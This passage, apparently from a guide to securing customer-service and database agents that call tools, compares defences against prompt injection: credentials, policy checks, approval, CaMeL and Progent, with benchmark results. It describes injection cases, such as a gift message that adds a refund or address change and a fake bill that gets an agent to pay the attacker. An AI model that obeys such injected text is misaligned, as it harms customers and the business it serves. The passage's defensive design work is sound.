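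The refund and the address change need different checks. For a refund, host code can look up the payment and calculate the largest permissible amount, so it can judge the request by its values. For an address change, the check should be whether the customer supplied the new address, because an address can be almost any text and a stranger's looks just like the customer's.

### Checks outside the model

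*A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* lists least privilege, structured tool APIs, human approval, sandboxing and transaction logs as defences for agents that use tools. No single layer is enough, because each of them lets some bad requests through:

| Layer | Example of what it stops | Example of what it lets through |
|---|---|---|
| Narrow credential | deleting an account with a token that can only read orders and request refunds | a refund on the wrong order |
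| Authorization in the API | customer 77 reading order 1024 | an unwanted change to the customer's own order |
| Policy check on each request | a refund larger than the price paid | a permitted refund that nobody asked for |
| Network limit | a request to attacker.example | misuse of the shop's own API |
| Human approval | a request that the approver recognises as wrong | a request approved out of habit |
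| Log of the request sent | nothing at the time | everything, but staff can find it later |

#### Credentials and authorization

An agent often acts with its user's own credentials and so can do everything the user can. Wibowo and Polyzos (2025), in *Toward a Safe Internet of Agents*, recommend a delegated credential instead. It permits an action only if the user may do it, the agent's registration covers it and the limits of the current session allow it. If $U$, $A$ and $S$ are the sets of actions that each of these permits, the agent may perform only those in

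$$U \cap A \cap S$$

This would stop an injected instruction to delete customer 77's account during that customer's own chat, because the support agent isn't registered for deletions. An ownership check could let the same instruction through.

#### Policy checks

A policy check can use facts that neither the credential nor the tool schema contains, such as the price paid, the number of refunds this month and whether the goods were returned. OpenAI compares the agent to a human support worker, whom customers sometimes deceive or threaten. Employers therefore use software to limit how much a worker can refund to one customer, and the same limit works for an agent.

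Strict rules also block legitimate requests. *aiAuthZ* (2026) tested a gateway that let a banking agent pay only known payees. The gateway blocked seven calls that served the attacker, but no attack succeeded even without it, because both models resisted the attacks well enough. The share of ordinary tasks completed fell from 100% to 80% because the gateway refused a legitimate first payment to a new payee. Each condition had only 20 pairs of task and attack, so the size of the loss is uncertain. A shop could reduce the loss by sending unusual requests to a person instead of refusing them.

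#### Network limits

A network limit still works if the host code misreads a URL or model-written code escapes from its sandbox. It does not restrict requests to permitted servers, so it matters most for tools that accept URLs or code.

#### Human approval

People approve requests carelessly if they see too many. Wibowo and Polyzos warn that an attacker can hide a harmful action in a stream of harmless ones. Approval therefore works best for rare actions that are hard to undo. The approver should see the request itself, such as "Refund $40 for order 1042 to the original card", and host code should send exactly that request without asking the model to write it again.

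The designer also has to choose who gives approval. The customer should confirm a new delivery address, but an employee should approve a large refund, since a dishonest customer would approve it.

#### Logs

The log should record the method, URL and body that the host code sent, the user and session, the result of each check and the API's response. It should not include tokens. The model's own summary is a poor substitute for the log, since it seldom revealed the leak in the eBay experiment. The agent also needs its own identity. Otherwise, as Wibowo and Polyzos point out, an auditor can't tell its actions from the user's.

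### Deciding on actions before reading untrusted text

These checks apply to requests the model has already written. The designer can also arrange the agent so that untrusted text has less influence on what the model writes. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe several patterns, three of which do this, each giving the model more freedom than the one before.

In the strictest pattern, the action-selector, the model only chooses among prepared actions. For a customer-service chatbot, the researchers suggest comparing each incoming message with a list of acceptable requests and acting only on a close match. The chatbot then can't help customers with legitimate requests that the developers didn't foresee.

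In the plan-then-execute pattern, the model writes a fixed list of tool calls before it reads any untrusted data. If a customer asks for an email with the details of order 1042, the plan is to fetch the order and then send the email to the address on file. A gift message in the order can't add a refund to the plan, but it can still change the wording of the email, because the model writes the email after reading the order.

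The code-then-execute pattern replaces the list with a program, which can include conditions and loops and can pass untrusted text to a separate model that has no tools. The agent can then handle requests such as "If my order is late, cancel it", where the next action depends on a reply that the planning model never sees.

#### What a database agent gives up

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues consider an agent that answers questions from SQL databases and writes Python to analyse the results, a task much like the shop's sales report. With no restrictions, the agent can check its results and write a better query if they don't answer the question. But an instruction stored in the database can also reach the model and lead it to extract data, change records or run harmful code.

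Query templates would avoid this, but employees could then get only the reports that someone had prepared. The researchers instead suggest that the model write the query and the analysis code without ever reading the data. The agent can still write one query for a new question and code to analyse the results and draw a chart, but it can no longer judge whether the results are sufficient. For example, if the shop's database spells a season "AUT" and the query looks for "autumn", the employee gets an empty chart and has to work out why.

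Host code could reduce this loss by returning only the number of rows. A number can't contain an instruction, and a count of zero would be enough for the model to try again.

The researchers judge that a sandbox with only the necessary connections does not reduce usefulness, but private data can still appear in the analysis or the chart. They consider it impractical to ask the user to approve every step, because the number of approvals grows with every question and every repeated query. Automatic filters need less attention but sometimes block legitimate work.

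None of this protects against the person asking the question. An employee could ask for everyone's salary, so the database still has to enforce that employee's permissions.

### CaMeL checks where a value came from

A fixed plan leaves one gap. Suppose a customer writes, "Change the address on order 1042 to the one in my sister's email." The plan is correct, but someone other than the customer wrote its most important value, the new address.

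CaMeL, a 2025 design from Google DeepMind, follows the code-then-execute pattern and adds a check on such values. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works. A "privileged" model reads only the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. In the shop, that program might be:

```
email = find_email(sender="sister")
address = ask_reader("Extract the delivery address", email)
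change_address(order_id="1042", address=address)
```

The function called `ask_reader` here passes the email to a "quarantined" model, which extracts the address but has no tools. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls. The privileged model never sees the email, so an instruction in the email can't add a fourth line to the program. It can at most change the contents of `address`.

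The interpreter attaches two labels to every value, one for its sources and one for who may read it. Before each tool call, it runs a policy, a short Python function that receives the arguments with their labels and allows or refuses the call. The policy for `change_address` could require the address to come from the customer's own message:

| Argument | Value | Source | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
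| `order_id` | 1042 | customer's message | allowed |
| `address` | 12 Mill Lane | email, through the quarantined model | refused |

The label for readers records who may read a piece of data. If only the customer and the courier may read a delivery address, a policy can block a program from posting it as a product review.

The address policy also blocks this customer's legitimate request, because the label records only that the address came from an email, not whether an attacker altered the email. The shop could ask the customer to confirm the address, but someone has to write that exception and a policy for every other sensitive tool.

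CaMeL applies its policies to one call at a time, which makes it awkward to enforce a rule about the order of calls, such as "confirm the return before refunding." Nikolaou and colleagues also check the whole program before any tool runs. Their software converts the program into a diagram of every path it could take and looks for a path that breaks a rule. If it finds one, it sends the privileged model a description of that path so the model can repair the program. The check simplifies loops, so it sometimes rejects a safe program.

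### Progent checks which values the task needs

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, control tool calls with rules about their names and values. Progent sits between the agent and its tools, so developers don't have to rebuild the agent as they would for CaMeL. For a customer who wants a refund on order 1042, the rules could be:

```
allow get_order       when order_id = "1042"
allow request_refund  when order_id = "1042" and amount <= 40
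```

Progent blocks any call that matches no rule. If a gift message leads the model to try to change the delivery address, the call fails because no rule covers that tool. A refund on order 1057 fails because no rule allows that value.

A language model writes the first rules from the user's request and proposes changes as the agent learns more. Injected text could manipulate that model too, so Progent doesn't apply every proposal automatically. It uses an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions, to check whether the new rules would allow any call that the old ones would refuse. If not, the change only narrows the agent's permissions and takes effect immediately. Lowering the refund limit to $25 is such a change. Adding a rule for `change_address` would expand the permissions, so it needs approval, either from a person or through a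 setting chosen in advance.

Both designs assume that the user is trustworthy, which isn't true of every customer in a public chat. A dishonest customer could ask for a refund on somebody else's order, and Progent's model might write a rule that permits it. Developers can prevent this with general rules that task-specific rules can't override. The ownership check and the refund limit belong in those general rules or in the shop's API.

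### How the two designs performed

AgentDojo, a common prompt-injection benchmark, simulates tasks in banking, Slack, travel and office work, with attackers' text in some of the tool results. According to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), CaMeL stopped nearly all of AgentDojo's attacks and completed a comparable share of tasks.

In Shi and colleagues' tests with GPT-4o, Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) gives the corresponding task completion rates: 76.3% with Progent and 79.4% without it when there was no attack, and 61.3% with Progent and 54.0% without it under attack. On ASB, another benchmark, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%.

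A simpler defence, which removed whole tools and ignored their arguments, blocked more useful work and let more attacks through. This is direct evidence for checking argument values as well as tool names.

The 1.0% mainly measures how well GPT-4o wrote the rules, not how well the approval step works, because Shi and colleagues approved every expansion automatically in that test to represent a careless user. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) raises the concern that adversarial text in a tool result could loosen the rules, which is possible when approval is automatic. When a person reviewed the first rules and every expansion, no attacks succeeded. Only 6% of the changes were expansions, so the reviewer would have had little to do.

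#### A later test with adaptive attacks

AgentDojo's attacks use fixed wording, so a defence that stops them might not stop a reworded version. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested ten defences on 57 AgentDojo tasks, excluding office work. A language model rewrote each attack over six rounds, with the attack's success count as its only feedback.

The table gives the percentage of tasks completed without an attack, followed by the success rate of the fixed or the rewritten attacks, whichever was higher:

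| Model | No defence | Progent | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o mini | 66.7 / 58.6 | 63.2 / 8.2 | 26.3 / 0.0 |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 77.2 / 8.7 | 73.7 / 1.8 | 52.6 / 1.8 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 63.2 / 50.4 | 57.9 / 3.6 | 28.1 / 0.3 |
| DeepSeek-v4-Flash | 89.5 / 22.6 | 78.9 / 4.6 | 38.6 / 0.8 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.2 / 1.8 | 63.2 / 0.5 | 40.4 / 0.5 |

Both designs held up against the rewritten attacks, but PIGuard, a filter that removes suspicious sentences from tool results, did not. On GPT-4o mini, it stopped every fixed attack but let 28% of the rewritten ones through. One that got through looked like an ordinary bill with new payment details. It contained no obvious instruction for the filter to find, and the agent paid the attacker.

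CaMeL reduced task completion far more than the earlier summary suggests, and much of the loss came from particular kinds of task. With GPT-5.4-mini and Claude Haiku 4.5, it didn't reduce completion on the travel tasks, most of which the user specified completely. On the Slack tasks, where the agent usually had to get some of the details from messages or web pages, completion fell from 95% to 43% and 24%. The other three models did complete fewer travel tasks with CaMeL. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) predicts that these losses will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code, but better planning won't help when a policy refuses a legitimate value because of its source.

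Progent reduced task completion only slightly elsewhere, but on AgentDyn, a benchmark with more open-ended tasks, it cut completion from 46.7% to 6.7% with GPT-4o mini and from 36.7% to 1.7% with Gemini 2.5 Flash. AgentDyn reports that CaMeL completed no tasks, so its perfect security score there means little. ROPE, a narrower source check that covers only each tool's sensitive parameters, still allowed the two models to complete 43.3% and 25.0% of tasks, respectively, and let through less than 3% of attacks. However, some researchers developed both ROPE and AutoDojo, so an independent test would be more convincing.

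The results also suggest that a designer should consider how much the user leaves open. Without a defence, fixed attacks on GPT-4o mini succeeded in 43% of cases where the user had specified everything and in 88% where the user had told the agent to do whatever some document said, though there were only 24 cases of the second kind. The shop's agent should therefore be more willing to act on "Refund order 1042" than on "Do what the courier's email says".

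### The case for a general request tool

The main objection to limited access is practical. A large API may need hundreds of narrow tools, and each one needs a description, a schema, tests and an owner who updates it when the API changes. Models also choose less accurately when they have more tools to choose from. *From REST to MCP* (2025) cites a study in which performance fell by 7% to 85% as the number of tools grew. Eventually a customer needs something the tools don't cover, and the team adds `shop_request(method, path, body)` for everything else.

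Bechard, Marquez Ayala and colleagues (2026), in *Terminal Agents Suffice for Enterprise Automation*, provide the strongest evidence for this objection. They compared agents that used existing MCP servers with agents that had a command line and wrote their own API requests. With Claude Sonnet 4.6, the agents completed these percentages of tasks:

| Platform | MCP tools | With MCP tools | With a command line |
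|---|---|---|---|
| ServiceNow (IT support) | 83 | 11.5 | 73.6 |
| GitLab | 81 | 45.2 | 76.5 |
| ERPNext (business records) | 7 | 55.6 | 67.6 |

The gap was also large with the three other models, and the average cost per task was similar for Sonnet. One ServiceNow task was to order an iPad. One agent found the item in the catalogue but had no tool for placing an order, so it opened a support ticket and failed the task. The command-line agent made several bad requests before it found one that worked.

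ERPNext's seven tools came closest to the command line because they could read and change any type of record. They have few parameters but give the model nearly as much access as a free path would.

Bechard and colleagues didn't add missing tools to the MCP servers they used. Their results therefore show that models perform badly when tools are missing, but not that they perform badly with narrow tools that cover the task. The study measured success, cost, tool calls and time, but didn't test attacks or count harmful side effects.

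A better experiment would keep the available operations the same and change only how much of each call the model writes. Bechard and colleagues also tried a single generic tool, but such a tool changes both how much the model writes and which operations it can reach. The benchmark by Maninger and colleagues comes closer because it gave models the same tasks with and without the correct endpoint. But it supplied that endpoint instead of making the model choose a tool, and it measured accuracy, not resistance to attack.

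### Grouped tools and mixed designs

A team can reduce the number of tools without letting the model write requests. For example, one tool can cover several related reads:

```
read_order(order_id, part)   part: "status", "items", "invoice" or "return"
```

The host code maps each value of `part` to a fixed request. Changes to an order should go in a separate tool so that the shop can require another permission or an approval for them. If there are hundreds of groups, the agent can search for the relevant tools and load only those.

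A designer can also base tools on how customers talk rather than on the API's endpoints. *Agent-First Tool API* (2026) tested tools that accept a description and return matching records, so the model doesn't have to guess an identifier. In the shop, a customer could ask about "the blue tent", and the host code would search that customer's orders. Failures from ambiguous requests fell from 28% to 4%, and average API calls fell from 4.8 to 3.2. The design's own developers reported these figures, using a single model.

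A mixed design keeps narrow tools for risky operations and gives the model more freedom elsewhere, for example by letting it write its own GraphQL reads but use only predefined writes. The free part must not be able to perform the guarded operations. If `request_refund` has a limit of $40 but `shop_request` can post to the refund endpoint with the same token, the model can bypass the limit. It could do so even without an attack, since many models try a more powerful tool after a narrow one fails. The general tool therefore needs its own credential, and the refund limit should be in the API or in host code that every request passes through.

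The objection still holds for work that nobody can list in advance. An engineer who manages a large cloud account may need any of thousands of endpoints, and an analyst's next question may need a query that no colleague has written. Narrow tools would either block much of this work or end up duplicating the API. Extensive access is reasonable here if the agent has only the permissions the person needs for the job, the data contains little text from outsiders, and somebody reviews changes that are hard to undo.

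A general request tool also suits the early stage of a project, when the team doesn't yet know what users will ask for. The team can try the tool on test data, log the agent's requests, and turn the most common ones into the first narrow tools.
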